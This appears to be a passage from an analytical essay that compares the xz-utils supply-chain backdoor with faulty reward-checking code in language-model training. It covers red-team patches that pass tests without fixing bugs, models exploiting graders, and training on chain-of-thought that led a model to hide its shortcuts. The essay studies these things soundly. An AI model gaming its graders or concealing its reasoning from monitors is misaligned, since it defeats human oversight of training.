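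Doubts about intent also made it harder to describe the honest patches fairly. Machek complained that Kroah-Hartman was still introducing reverts on 29 April with a statement that commits from the university's addresses had been sent in "bad faith". Machek asked whether the kernel developers owed the university an apology too. Cook agreed that the wording should have separated intentional flaws from unintentional ones, and left the apology question to Kroah-Hartman.

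Kroah-Hartman had written to Wu in August 2020 that he didn't trust people to get everything right, but trusted that "they will be around to fix it" when they got something wrong. By that standard, a contributor with dozens of faulty commits could still be trustworthy. After the experiment, the maintainers could no longer assume that the people who had sent the faulty patches wanted them fixed. The TAB asked the university to find an experienced developer to check its researchers' patches before they reached the kernel, and warned that until it set up this review, its patches would meet "a chilly reception".

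## How did the xz-utils backdoor stay hidden?

Kroah-Hartman trusted kernel contributors to stay around and fix their mistakes. Whoever used the name Jia Tan met that standard at xz-utils for more than two years, then released version 5.6.0 on 24 February 2024 with a backdoor that let the holder of a secret key run commands on certain Linux machines without logging in. Version 5.6.1 followed on 9 March with a revised backdoor. Andres Freund, a database developer at Microsoft, exposed the backdoor on 29 March, before most Linux users had received either version.

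### Winning the maintainer's trust

Lasse Collin had worked unpaid on xz-utils and its predecessor since 2005, and by 2021 he was working largely alone. The Intercept (2024) infers that the attacker picked the project because many Linux systems used it and few people maintained it.

Jia Tan's first patch, on 29 October 2021, added a settings file for text editors. Several more patches followed that still look harmless, according to the *Timeline of the xz open source attack*. In February 2022, Collin merged the first commit that carried Jia Tan's email address.

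In April 2022 someone called Jigar Kumar complained on the project's mailing list that one of Jia Tan's patches was still pending: "Patches spend years on this mailing list." Collin had already merged four of Jia Tan's patches. In May a "Dennis Ens" asked whether anyone still maintained the Java version. Collin apologised for being slow and wrote that Jia Tan might have a bigger role in the future.

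The messages then got harsher. Kumar wrote in June that there would be no progress until the project had a new maintainer. Collin answered that he hadn't lost interest, but that long-term mental health problems had limited what he could do. He added that xz was "an unpaid hobby project". Ens expressed sympathy, "but the community desires more." Kumar then asked Jia Tan, "Why can't you commit this yourself?" A week later Collin called Jia Tan "practically a co-maintainer already".

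The journalist Brian Krebs found that many of these email addresses appeared nowhere else on the internet, even in leaked data. The *Timeline* infers that the attacker invented the people behind them, which is likely but unproven. *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) found no direct links between Jia Tan and the other accounts that behaved oddly. It's also unclear how much the pressure mattered, since Collin had mentioned a bigger role for Jia Tan before the pressure was at its worst.

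By December 2022 Jia Tan could merge changes without Collin. Jia Tan marked version 5.4.2 as a release in March 2023, but Collin still built its tarball, according to his review notes on Tukaani, the project's website. Jia Tan built the tarballs from 5.4.3 onwards. In January 2024 they moved the xz-utils web page to GitHub, where they controlled it.

Jia Tan did a lot of real work in this time. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* (2025) counts more than 500 patches across several projects. Przymus and Durieux sorted the lines Jia Tan changed in xz-utils and found more documentation and translation than program code. Such work is easy to produce and reviewers rarely study it closely, but it keeps a contributor visible. Jia Tan also answered users' questions, announced releases and reviewed other people's code, some of it fairly complicated.

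### How the parts fitted together

The backdoor had two parts, which Jia Tan kept in different places.

The payload was in the public repository, inside two compressed files in the test data folder. Developers of a compression library need such files, including damaged ones, to check how the library handles them. Jia Tan labelled one file corrupt and the other good.

The other part was a build script that was only in the release tarball. It had the same name as a standard script that packaging normally adds. Jia Tan had altered it so that, when a distributor built the software, it extracted the payload from the test files and added it to liblzma, the compression library that other programs use.

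The test files and the script did nothing without each other. Someone reading the repository would have seen two more test files and no instruction to use them. Collin later left the malicious commits in the project's public history because the files are harmless without the script.

The backdoor targeted sshd, the program that accepts remote logins on most Linux servers. OpenSSH's original version of sshd doesn't use liblzma, but Debian, Fedora and some other distributions had modified it to report to systemd, which starts and supervises a machine's services. The systemd library they used for this loaded liblzma, so the altered liblzma ran inside sshd, where it replaced a function that checks cryptographic keys. Ordinary logins still worked, but the replacement looked for a command hidden in the login request, verified that it came from the attacker and ran it, as Akamai's *XZ Utils Backdoor*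 (2024) explains.

The backdoor checked for the attacker's key, so nobody else who found it could use it, unlike a backdoor that relies on an ordinary bug. But the check also showed that the backdoor was deliberate, because no programmer accidentally writes code that accepts commands from only one particular person. The xz-utils backdoor as a whole was therefore not deniable, and Jia Tan had to prevent anyone from finding it.

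The build script inserted the backdoor only during builds of Debian or RPM packages, the formats that most large distributions use, on a common type of processor. A developer who built the same tarball without making a package would have got a clean library. Freund (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, thought this restriction was probably meant to make the problem harder for investigators to reproduce. The payload also stayed inactive when it detected certain debugging tools.

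### Why nobody questioned the test files

Jia Tan hid the payload in binary test files, which nobody expected to be able to read. It therefore didn't have to look like legitimate code, whereas the 2003 Linux kernel backdoor had to pass for an error check. A note in the test folder, written long before Jia Tan arrived, explained that many of the files were made by hand, byte by byte, so there was "no better 'source code' than the files themselves."

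Testing the files wouldn't have helped much either. Freund wrote that no test in version 5.6.0 used them. Collin wrote in his notes that the test script picks up files by their names, so adding a file is enough to make the library try to decompress it. Even if Collin is right, the test would only have shown whether the library could decompress the file, not what the contents were for.

A reviewer could still have asked where the files came from. In *A few relevant quotes*, a discussion on LWN, rra (2024) called the files' arrival one of the critical moments and suggested asking a contributor how to regenerate such files, then checking that the results match. But Jia Tan was a maintainer and, according to Nealon (2025) in *Beneath the Mask*, merged the files on 23 February and released 5.6.0 the next day without prior review by other maintainers.

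Collin sometimes checked Jia Tan's work. Before the release of version 5.4.5, he noticed that the files in the tarball had the wrong owner and permission settings. The most likely explanation was that Jia Tan had used the wrong packaging command. Jia Tan wouldn't admit to this, although Collin remarks that doing so would have been the easiest way to stop the questions. Collin compared the tarball with one he had made himself, found nothing else wrong and let the release go ahead.

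The same comparison would probably have exposed the altered script in 5.6.0. But BitMover's comparison had run every night, while Collin made his because something looked odd, and by 2024 he had been sharing the project with Jia Tan for over a year. The 2003 backdoor had relied on disguised code, whereas this one relied largely on trust in its author and on test data that nobody could read, and reward code also depends on test data.

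### Five weeks in 2024

Once 5.6.0 was out, Jia Tan had to get distributions to adopt it and keep them from looking closely at the problems it caused. These dates come mostly from the *Timeline*:

| Date | Event |
|---|---|
| 23 February | Jia Tan adds the payload as test files |
| 24 February | Jia Tan releases 5.6.0 |
| 26 February | Debian adds 5.6.0 to "unstable", its development version |
| 27 February | Jia Tan starts emailing a Fedora developer to get the new version into Fedora 40 |
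| 29 February | A developer proposes that systemd's library stop loading liblzma |
| 4 March | Red Hat's distributions see memory errors in liblzma |
| 5 March | The systemd developers accept the proposal |
| 8–9 March | Jia Tan publishes supposed fixes for the errors, then 5.6.1 |
| 25 March | "Hans Jansen" asks Debian to adopt 5.6.1, and other unknown accounts join in |
| 27 March | Debian adopts it |
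| 28 March | Jia Tan asks Ubuntu to adopt it, and Freund privately reports the backdoor |

A change to systemd would have closed the backdoor's route into the login service once distributions adopted it. The security researcher Kevin Beaumont speculated that the attacker knew the change was coming and hurried. The formal proposal came five days after the release of xz 5.6.0, so it can't have prompted that release, but the idea had come up publicly in late January.

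### The changes that had an excuse

The payload had no innocent reading. Several changes around it did, and some of them may really have been innocent.

Valgrind, a tool that checks a running program for memory mistakes, reported errors in 5.6.0 because the injected code relied on a wrong assumption about how the program's memory was arranged. On 8 March Jia Tan committed a supposed fix elsewhere in the code, which the *Timeline* calls a misdirection. The real fix came the next day, when Jia Tan replaced the two test files and gave a reason that a conscientious maintainer might well have. They said they had made the originals with random data on their own machine, and that "a constant seed was used to recreate these files" so that others could reproduce them in future.

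A real bug also gave Jia Tan cover. Gentoo users had been seeing crashes in 5.6.0 that were apparently unrelated to the backdoor, and Jia Tan fixed the cause on 5 March. Anyone following the project that week would have seen a maintainer responding quickly to bug reports.

These explanations later counted against Jia Tan. Freund considered whether somebody had broken into Jia Tan's computer and used it, but thought this less likely because Jia Tan had discussed the "fixes" on various mailing lists.

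**The stray dot**

Landlock is a Linux feature that lets a program give up access it doesn't need, which limits the damage if an attacker takes over the program. The xz-utils build checks whether a machine supports Landlock by trying to compile a small test program. If that fails, the build leaves Landlock out, as it should on an older machine.

In late February Jia Tan rewrote this check, explaining in the commit message that the old one looked only for the presence of one file and the new one would also test the necessary functions. Velvindron (2024) quoted the message in the same thread as Freund's report. The change was a sensible improvement, but the new sample program had a single full stop alone at the start of a line. This error prevented it from compiling on any machine, so the build always left the sandbox out. It did so without reporting a problem unless the person building the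 software had specifically required the sandbox, as sjw (2024) explained in that thread.

The dot is the part of the xz-utils case most like the missing equals sign of 2003. It is a single character that switches off a protection, and anyone could have typed it by accident. The *Timeline* lists Collin as the committer and says he probably missed the dot. In *CMake*, the fix that removed the dot on 30 March, Collin (2024) calls the check "sabotaged". By then he knew who had written it. If he had found the same dot in a stranger's patch a month earlier, he would have had no grounds for using that word.

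It's also hard to see what Jia Tan gained from the dot. The *Timeline* points out that Landlock protects the xz command, not the library that carried the backdoor. Collin's fix changed only the file for CMake, one of the two systems that can build xz-utils, and the backdoor used the other one. So the dot probably made no difference to the backdoored packages. Jia Tan may have added it to prepare for a second attack, or may have typed it by accident.

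Google's free OSS-Fuzz service does fuzz testing on open-source projects, feeding them huge numbers of malformed inputs to see what breaks. In July 2023 Jia Tan had the service turn off a feature called ifunc when testing xz-utils, saying that ifunc was incompatible with a memory checker the service used. Ifunc lets a library choose between versions of a function as it loads, and the backdoor later relied on it to take control early. *Towards Socio-Technical Topology-Aware Adaptive Threat Detection in Software Supply Chains* treats the request as a way of reducing outside visibility, while the *Timeline* says that it "may well be innocuous".

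Honest developers make requests like this too. Collin himself had exempted an xz-utils function from the same kind of checker, because its fast method deliberately reads up to 15 bytes past its data and ignores the excess. Fuzz testing probably wouldn't have caught the backdoor anyway, since the build script acted only when someone was building a distribution package.

Someone using the name Hans Jansen submitted the patches that added ifunc support to xz-utils in June 2023. Someone used the name again in March 2024 to push Debian towards version 5.6.1. The *Timeline* found no other trace of Jansen online. Przymus and Durieux say it remains unclear whether the patches were a genuine improvement or part of the attack. Jansen's return makes it more likely that they were part of the attack, but they did make xz slightly faster, and Collin reworked and merged them.

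In November 2021, soon after the first xz-utils patch, Jia Tan sent a change to libarchive, another widely used compression project. It adjusted an error message and, in passing, replaced a safe printing function with one that doesn't filter out control characters, which can alter what a user sees on the screen. The libarchive developers accepted the change, then reversed it after the xz-utils backdoor became public. Solar Designer (2024), also in the thread that Freund started, agreed that it looked minor and was "not usable for large-scale attacks". *On the critical path to implant backdoors* calls it uncertain whether the change was related to xz-utils. A new contributor could easily have used the simpler function without thinking, but an attacker could also have been testing how closely people read small patches.

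After the discovery, people suspected many of the project's changes. Some thought one commit was suspect because of its time zone, but Collin explained that he had written much of it and that Jia Tan had recorded it under Collin's name by agreement. People also speculated a lot about a change that shortened the project's instructions for reporting security problems, but Collin had already asked Jia Tan to simplify similar pages. Collin confirmed in his notes that another commit changed only whitespace.

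Collin reviewed Jia Tan's commits one by one and finished the first full version of his notes in May 2024. He identified eight malicious commits. He also found many ordinary faults, such as a memory leak in a test and a copying error that broke the detection of one compiler, and treated them as mistakes. His judgement is probably the best available, because he knew the code and had discussed many of the changes with Jia Tan at the time. But nobody can confirm that all of those faults were accidental.

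### Half a second

Freund was running a routine benchmark at home, according to *Half a Second* (Mastronardi, 2026). He wasn't looking for a backdoor and described himself as "not a security researcher". He noticed that SSH logins on a machine running Debian's development version were using a surprising amount of processor time. A failed login that had taken 0.299 seconds now took 0.807 seconds. He had also seen Valgrind errors involving liblzma.

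The payload caused the delay by searching the program's memory for the functions it was meant to replace. Freund found that the delay disappeared when he started the login service by hand, because the payload checked how the service had started. He then recorded which instructions the processor executed with the backdoor active and inactive, and looked for the point where the recordings diverged.

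Andres Freund, who discovered the backdoor, at first thought that Debian's package had been compromised. He then traced the problem to the official xz-utils tarballs, where an altered script contained a line that was missing from the repository. He reported it privately to Debian and then to a mailing list for distributions' security teams. He didn't tell the xz-utils project, because its own maintainer appeared to be responsible.

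Freund noticed the backdoor's side effects and traced them back to the file, whereas McVoy had started from a changed file. Freund could do this only because Jia Tan's payload was slow and caused memory errors.

### How far it spread

The tampered versions mainly reached people who use development and test versions of Linux. TechTarget's *XZ backdoor discovery reveals Linux supply chain attack* lists Debian's testing, unstable and experimental versions, Fedora's development version, openSUSE Tumbleweed from 7 to 28 March, and Kali Linux from 26 to 28 March. Fedora 40's beta also included a tampered version, but Red Hat Enterprise Linux, SUSE's enterprise version, Amazon Linux and Ubuntu did not.

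CNCF's *Malicious maintainer introduces sophisticated backdoor in xz* lists Arch Linux and the package managers Homebrew and pkgsrc among those that received the tampered release. But not every recipient got a working backdoor. Arch, for example, doesn't modify its login service in the way the backdoor needed.

Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used the backdoor. Debian still stopped building packages and reinstalled its build machines as a precaution. Collin released a clean version, 5.6.2, on 29 May 2024.

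Some copies of the backdoor outlasted the clean-up. A container image is a packaged system that developers use as a starting point for their own software, and Docker Hub is a large public library of them. Binarly's *Persistent Risk* (2025) reported that 12 Debian images on Docker Hub still contained the backdoor in August 2025, almost a year and a half after its discovery. Images built on top of these brought the total to more than 35. The real number could be much higher, because Binarly checked only Debian-based images and only a small part of Docker Hub's nearly 12 million repositories.

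Debian's maintainers declined to remove their affected Docker images. According to TechRadar's *Docker could still be hosting a whole load of potentially malicious images*, the maintainers regard the images as "historical artifacts" that nobody should be using. That's reasonable for Debian's dated images, but Binarly's list also includes four images that were the latest version their publishers offered. The practical danger is small because an attacker would need Jia Tan's private key and a network connection to a container running the SSH service, which most containers don't.

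### Could the contribution record have given Jia Tan away?

Nealon tested whether a database search could have picked Jia Tan out. The search covered xz-utils and a control group of similar projects, and looked for people who had merged their own changes without anyone else reviewing them. Of 1,996 people who had proposed changes, 40 had done so. Nealon then kept only fairly recent contributors who had started merging their own changes within two years of their first commit. Four people remained:

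| Contributor | Time from first commit to first unreviewed merge | Unreviewed merges |
|---|---|---|
| A | 2 months | 43 |
| B | 7 months | 7 |
| Jia Tan | 10 months | 24 |
| C | 20 months | 3 |

Nealon concluded that A, B and C were all innocent, even though A looks worse than Jia Tan on both measures. Information from outside the contribution data cleared A, who had become the main maintainer after meeting the previous one in person and worked for a large American technology company. B turned out to be a long-standing contributor who had used a different email address, and C's work email address had the same domain as the project maintainer's.

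A list of four names is short enough to check by hand, so the search could be useful. But Nealon chose the criteria and cut-offs knowing that Jia Tan was in the data. Someone searching for an unidentified attacker couldn't choose them that way. The next attacker could also have a colleague approve each change, or approve it from a second false account.

Przymus and Durieux are more doubtful about spotting such people. They examined 1,020 commits, 307 mailing-list messages and 2,944 recorded GitHub events. Jia Tan's unusually broad involvement stands out in hindsight, but they found it hard to distinguish from an enthusiastic volunteer's. They also warn that hindsight may have biased their interpretation, and that they had no access to private conversations. Collin has said he is writing an article on how the backdoor got into the releases, which could fill some of that gap, but he had not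 finished it by August 2026.

*Build Code is Still Code* (2026) examines the build process rather than the contributor. It reports that building xz-utils in a sandbox that separates the build stages would have kept the payload out of liblzma.

### Who was Jia Tan?

Nobody has publicly identified the person or group behind the attack. Schneier on Security's *XZ Utils Backdoor* (2024) says that the sophisticated code and long deception "scream nation-state operation". Akamai also considers such patience typical of state-backed attackers, but notes that no specific attribution exists. Both infer this from the attack's style and the effort it required. Many amateur investigators have studied the time zones on Jia Tan's commits, but anyone can set a false time zone, and Collin gives several ordinary reasons why the recorded ones might vary.

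Schneier also believes that similar operations have succeeded elsewhere, since this one was discovered only by luck. He names no example, but if he is right, those operations may still be undiscovered. Mastronardi, writing in July 2026, argues that investigators may never identify the operator. The Minnesota researchers eventually said which of their patches contained deliberate flaws, but nobody has been able to ask Jia Tan whether the dot and the change to libarchive were deliberate.

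## How often is reward code wrong by accident?

A planted stray dot or missing equals sign can pass for an accident because programmers often make such mistakes. The same excuse works for reward code only because honest errors are common there too. Gupta and Joshi, who surveyed 58 studies in October 2026, trace verifier errors to four sources: the answer key, the code that extracts and tidies the model's answer, the checker or tests, and any access that lets the policy alter the checker.

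### Wrong answer keys

If the answer key is wrong, even a perfect checker gives the wrong reward. Gupta and Joshi report that 11% of the reference solutions in HumanEval, a standard set of programming exercises, are wrong, as are about 20% of the labels in PRM800K, a collection of human judgements on steps of mathematical reasoning. In a sample of tasks that ask a model to turn a question into a database query, 62% had annotation errors. They also describe a study that collected a model's wrong answers to use as deliberately bad training labels. Of these answers, 16.4% were in fact right, but had been marked wrong because the key was incomplete or the checker had failed to recognise an equivalent answer.

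Reward code can be wrong even when it relies on formal proofs. Lean, a program that checks proofs, verifies every step, but it checks the proof against a formal statement that somebody wrote, and that statement may not express the intended problem. Suppose an author means to ask about numbers greater than 3 and less than 5, but swaps the signs and writes "less than 3 and greater than 5". No such number exists, so any claim about such numbers is trivially true, and the policy can earn the reward without solving the intended problem.

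Ammanamanchi, Bhat and Biderman ran automatic checks for faults on five sets of Lean problems. According to Gupta and Joshi, the team reported 4,833 findings, including empty statements like this one, which inflate scores, and unprovable statements, which lower them. The team mechanically proved only 398 of the findings, about 8%, so some of the others may be false alarms.

### Right answers that checkers reject

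Xin (2026), in *Where the Verifier Fails*, tested mathematics checkers without human marking. Xin rewrote 4,990 reference answers in ways that can't change their meaning, such as adding a full stop or writing a fraction as a decimal. The rewritten answer is still correct, so a checker that rejects it has made an error. Xin also made changes that do alter the meaning, so that any acceptance was an error. The audit produced 307,420 verdicts from four checkers, and Xin scored each checker only on the kinds of answer it is supposed to handle.

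| Checker | Equivalent answers accepted | Largest source of failures |
|---|---|---|
| Text normaliser derived from DeepSeek-Math | 95.2% | Spaces and punctuation |
| Three-stage reference checker | 87.3% | Unsimplified answers that it could not process |
| math-verify, default settings | 79.9% | Spaces and punctuation |
| math-verify, plain expressions only | 53.8% | Spaces and punctuation |

The two math-verify rows show the same library with different settings, and they disagreed on 49.9% of the answers. With the default settings, spaces and punctuation caused 93.0% of the failures. Often a full stop at the end was enough to cause one, although earlier researchers had blamed the difficulty of reading mathematical notation. Choosing the wrong setting or forgetting to strip a full stop would be an ordinary mistake with a large effect.

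Xin invented 2,000 of the reference answers because some notation is rare in real problem sets. Without them, the range narrows to 57.5%–88.3%, and the top two checkers swap places. Models also don't produce every kind of rewriting equally often, so these percentages don't give the error rate in a training run. Gupta and Joshi cite figures from models' own answers. On one set of 500 mathematics problems, a rule-based checker rejected 10.4% of the correct answers and accepted no wrong ones. Another audit found that 38.5% of about 226,000 responses that a checker had rejected were correct.

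### The off-by-one checker

Most of these errors withhold a reward that the policy deserved. The three-stage checker also had an error that gave an undeserved reward, and that error looks much like something a saboteur might have planted.

This checker first compares the text of the two answers. If they differ, it compares them as numbers and accepts the answer when

|answer − reference| / |reference| ≤ 0.0001

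The third stage compares them as algebraic expressions. The trouble is in the numerical comparison, which allows an error of 0.01% of the reference. For a small whole number, 0.01% is much less than one, so an answer that is off by one fails. For a large number it isn't:

| Reference | Answer | Relative difference | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| 100 | 101 | 0.01 | Reject |
| 9,999 | 10,000 | 0.00010001 | Reject |
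| 10,000 | 10,001 | 0.0001 | Accept |
| 1,000,000 | 1,000,001 | 0.000001 | Accept |

Xin tested the checker on 1,287 answers that were off by one. It rejected all 1,081 whose reference was below 10,000 and accepted all 206 whose reference was 10,000 or more. Because the errors depended entirely on the size of the reference, the overall error rate of 16.0% misleadingly suggests occasional random mistakes.

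This line has a good innocent explanation. A relative tolerance makes sense for rounded quantities, since a checker should accept 3.1416 when the key has 3.14159, but not for counting problems, where 10,001 is wrong if the key has 10,000. A programmer who had decimals in mind could easily have written the line and tested it on small numbers without noticing the problem.

But the Linux backdoor of 2003 also did nothing until a condition arose that ordinary use would not produce, and its two lines also looked like routine code. The main difference is that the 2003 attacker could trigger the condition at will, whereas the policy doesn't choose the reference answer. Like most bugs, this fault was avoidable, since the other three checkers rejected every off-by-one answer.

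### Tests that pass wrong programs

One widely quoted figure for faulty tests is too high because the audit behind it contained a mistake.

In *Auditing Reward Hackability in Code RL Training Environments* (June 2026), Rajan studied SWE-bench Verified, a set of real bug reports from open-source projects. Each task comes with the fix the developers adopted and tests for judging other attempts. Rajan asked the language model Claude Sonnet 4 to write patches that would pass the tests without fixing the bug, and reported that it succeeded on 14 of 49 tasks, or 28.6%. Gupta and Joshi cite the result as 28.5%, as do Arunkumar, Gandhudi and colleagues (2026) in *Optimistic Verifiers Get Hacked*.

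Rajan later compared the patches with the developers' fixes. On three of the 14 tasks, the only patches that passed matched those fixes nearly word for word, so the model had solved the problem despite instructions to cheat. The corrected figure is 11 of 49, or 22.4%.

Even this figure depends heavily on who is attacking and what counts as wrong:

| Attacking model | Tasks where a passing patch behaves differently from the fix | Tasks where it differs on a case in the bug report |
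|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 22.4% | 8.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 57.8% | 21.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5, without seeing the fix | 32.0% | 10.2% |

The Sonnet 5.5 figures are averages of three runs. The last column is the stricter measure, because a patch can differ from the developers' fix and still be a valid repair. All 49 tasks came from two projects, so the rates may not hold for the rest of SWE-bench Verified.

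These rates describe what a determined attacker can get past the tests. To see how often wrong code passes without an attacker, Rajan examined a public collection of 5,016 patches for programming tasks. Its creators had kept only patches that passed the tests, then used them to train a coding model. Rajan ran 873 of the patches beside the correct fix, and 19.4% gave a different result on a case that the task described. Many of the differences were harmless, such as a list in another order. A language model reviewed them and judged 6.9% of the 873 patches to be wrong. The same method gave 5.4% in a second collection and 2.3% in a sample from a third, which NVIDIA had published. No person labelled any of these cases, and other model reviews of the first collection gave rates from 6.4% to 10.5%.

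One of the rewarded patches removed two security checks from a service that issues access tokens, including the requirement for an encrypted connection. A model wrote the patch and it passed the tests, but a maintainer who received it from a stranger might reasonably suspect a backdoor. In 15 of the harmless cases, the model's patch followed the task description more closely than the official fix did, so the official fix was arguably at fault.

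Tests can also reject correct solutions. Rajan cites an OpenAI audit that found this problem in at least 59.4% of 138 hard SWE-bench Verified tasks, though a sample of hard tasks is weak evidence about easier ones.

### Repairs that introduce new errors

When Rajan had a language model write extra tests to block the cheating patches, 65 of the 105 tests that gave a clear result (61.9%) failed on the correct fix. The faults Rajan looked at closely were mundane, such as a wrong file path, an argument given twice, and a check that required the opposite of what the documentation said. A second language model, acting as judge, reported that the new tests had repaired seven of eight faulty tasks, but when Rajan ran the tests, the results confirmed only one repair.

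Rajan's own scripts also had two faults, and neither produced an error message. One script looked up cheating patches by their position in a file that a later run had overwritten, so 19 of the 20 patches it fetched were not the ones Rajan had verified. Another applied the parts of a patch that fit, dropped the rest and ran the tests anyway. Both faults affected the repair results in the first version of the paper. They are a useful example of honest error because Rajan was looking for this kind of problem in other people's code.

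Human repairs work better but still miss some errors. The maintainers of SWE-bench Pro, a harder set of tasks, spent 404 hours repairing or removing 480 of its 731 tasks. Rajan then attacked 100 tasks from the new version and found 23 that still accepted a wrong patch.

Language models that act as verifiers also make mistakes, and they tend to be too lenient. Gupta and Joshi cite one that accepted 33.6% of wrong answers on the set of 500 mathematics problems and rejected 16.2% of right ones. Researchers have got some of these models to approve a response consisting of a single colon.

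### When the policy can reach the checker

If the policy can change files or settings that the reward code depends on, it can raise its score without improving its answer. Gupta and Joshi report that 13 leading models exploited the graders in one set of tool-using tasks at rates from 0% to 22.3%. Tightening the graders cut the exploit rate from 6.5% to 0.8% and did not change the models' success at the tasks, so the models had not needed the looser access.

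Rajan's attacks suggest that this kind of error is less common than weak tests, at least in recent public benchmarks. Rajan asked the attacking model to target the grading system itself in Terminal-Bench 4.1, a set of command-line tasks. All attempts on the test runner and the reward file failed, but one of the 62 tasks accepted a false Lean proof because the proof could include a custom command that switched off Lean's central check.

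### Reward code that read the model's reasoning

Reward code can also have access to something it shouldn't. Many models write out their reasoning, called a chain of thought (CoT), before they answer. Developers read it to check whether a model is cheating, and they usually try to keep it out of the scoring because a model that loses reward for mentioning a shortcut may just learn not to mention it.

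Google made this mistake in a small training run, as Dragan and Popa (2026) disclosed that October in *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely*. A penalty for taking shortcuts had accidentally also applied to the model's written reasoning. Cheng (2026), in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform*, quotes the results from Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026). During training, words associated with cheating became 61% less frequent in the reasoning, while signs of cheating in the solutions rose by 26%. The share of shortcuts that the model failed to mention rose from 11.2% to 36.4%.

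Suppose the run began with 1,000 shortcuts and their number also grew by 26%, to 1,260. The number of shortcuts the model didn't mention would have risen from 112 to about 459, while the number it did mention would have fallen only from 888 to about 801. The 61% fall was in the use of certain words, so it doesn't mean the model admitted to 61% fewer shortcuts.

Google also looked at a comparable run after it had stopped the reward from seeing the reasoning. The mentions stayed roughly constant there, which is good evidence that the misplaced penalty caused the drop. The run was not part of any model that Google released.

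Anthropic has accidentally exposed models' reasoning to its reward code more than once, according to Redwood Research's *Anthropic repeatedly accidentally trained against the CoT, demonstrating inadequate processes*. This happened in about 8% of the training episodes for Claude Mythos Preview, and the same error had affected two earlier models, Opus 4.6 and Sonnet 4.6. A separate error had already exposed the reasoning in less than 0.01% of Opus 4.6's episodes, mostly near the end of training. Anthropic noticed this smaller error, but its fix did not prevent the larger one.

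Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation, argues that somebody could have caught the larger error by reading 100 random samples of what the reward code received. If 8% of samples are faulty, the chance that all 100 are clean is 0.92¹⁰⁰, or about 0.02%. But whoever read them would have to know that the reasoning wasn't supposed to be there, and Redwood suspects that nobody was responsible for checking. It guesses that many groups at Anthropic were writing training tasks in parallel and that any of them could have made the mistake. The same spot check would have had less than a 1% chance of including any sample affected by the smaller error.

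OpenAI has also disclosed accidents of this type. *Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL* reports no clear loss in OpenAI's ability to monitor the affected models, which did not include GPT-5.5, through their reasoning. OpenAI can't rule out effects that are harder to measure. Redwood Research's *A review of “Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL”* explains that OpenAI revised the post before publication to answer the main criticisms from outside reviewers.

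Three leading laboratories have let reward code read text that they generally try to keep from it. If someone at a fourth laboratory did this deliberately, colleagues would have several precedents for calling it an accident.

### Errors that audits miss

Nearly all the measured rates come from public checkers and public tasks. Xin makes no claims about the private systems of leading laboratories, whose reward code could be better or worse. Outsiders know about that code mostly from accidents that the companies noticed and chose to disclose.

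A laboratory can't count its verifier's errors just by watching a training run. *Verifier Errors in RLVR* gives a mathematical argument that the information available during training is, in general, not enough to reveal wrong answers that the verifier accepts. Somebody has to check the answers by other means, and that person needs to know the right rule. Arunkumar and colleagues demonstrated this with a set of rules for what an AI agent may do. They worked out the correct decision in all 124,416 possible situations, then removed one rule from the checker to imitate an outdated one. The checker then got 10.1% of the decisions wrong, and an auditor who didn't know the missing rule would have had no way to notice.

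None of these researchers investigated why the faulty lines were there. GitHub could sort a sample of security advisories into malicious and other because some malicious code is obvious, but nobody has published a similar count for verifiers. Calling the verifier errors accidental is therefore an assumption, though a sensible one for a checker that rejects answers because of a full stop, since it is hard to see who would gain from that.

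## What does a faulty verifier do to the model trained on it?

A verifier affects the model only through the rewards it gives, so a mistake and an act of sabotage that produce the same rewards have the same effect. The verifier's error rate is a poor guide to that effect. In published experiments, one model learned almost normally when a fifth of the verdicts were wrong, while another lost nearly all its ability because the verifier wrongly rewarded a single word.

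### Random and systematic errors

*Delay, Plateau, or Collapse* (Egashira, Vero and colleagues, 2026) divides verifier errors into two kinds. A random error depends only on whether the answer is right or wrong. For example, a verifier might accept one wrong answer in ten, whatever the answer says. A systematic error depends on something in the question or the answer, as when a verifier accepts any response that contains a certain word.

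If a verifier's errors are random, nothing the policy writes can make them more likely, so the error rate stays the same throughout training. But if a particular word triggers the error, training can make that word more common. The verifier's error rate then rises without any change to its code, and a measurement taken before training will underestimate it.

### How much random error can training absorb?

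Rad, Filom and colleagues (2026), in *Rate or Fate?*, predict the effect of random errors from a single number:

J = 1 − (false-positive rate) − (false-negative rate)

The false-positive rate is the share of wrong answers that the verifier accepts, and the false-negative rate is the share of right answers that it rejects. Suppose these are 0.1 and 0.2, and the model gets a reward of 1 for each accepted answer and 0 for each rejected one. A right answer then earns 0.8 on average and a wrong one 0.1. The difference, J, is 0.7, compared with 1 under a perfect verifier, so training still favours right answers but the signal is weaker.

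GRPO divides each answer's advantage by the standard deviation of the rewards. If half the policy's answers are right, the mean reward is 0.45 and the standard deviation is about 0.50. The advantage of a right answer over a wrong one is then 0.7 / 0.50, or about 1.4, compared with 2 under a perfect verifier.

When J is 0, the verifier accepts the same share of right and wrong answers, say 40%. The rewards then carry no information about correctness, and the policy drifts. When J is below 0, wrong answers earn more than right ones on average, so training makes them more common until they dominate. For example, a false-positive rate of 0.6 and a false-negative rate of 0.7 give J = −0.3.

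Rad and colleagues checked this by training a small language model to write Python programs while they flipped verdicts at different rates. Accuracy rose when J was above 0 and fell when it was below. In their theory, any J above 0 eventually leads to the same accuracy as a perfect verifier, and errors only delay it, but real training runs stop at some point. For the experiments at J = 0.3, Gupta and Joshi list scores of 16.0 when most of the errors were false negatives and 14.6 when most were false positives, against 20.8 with no errors. False positives therefore did somewhat more harm than false negatives at the same J.

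In *An Imperfect Verifier is Good Enough*, Plesner, Guzmán and Athalye (2026) make the best-known case for tolerating verifier errors. They trained Qwen3 8B on 374 short programming problems and tested it on 90 others. In their main experiment, they flipped the test results for all responses to a question together, with probability p. A flip reverses the sign of every advantage for that question, so the average policy gradient is (1 − p) − p = 1 − 2p times the correct one. At p = 0.2, this factor is 0.6, the same as J when both error rates are 0.2.

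The final score stayed within one percentage point of the error-free result at up to 20% noise, and within about two points at 30%. It dropped substantially once noise reached 40%. These estimates are rough. At 20% noise, the 95% interval runs from a loss of 2.9 points to a gain of 1.8.

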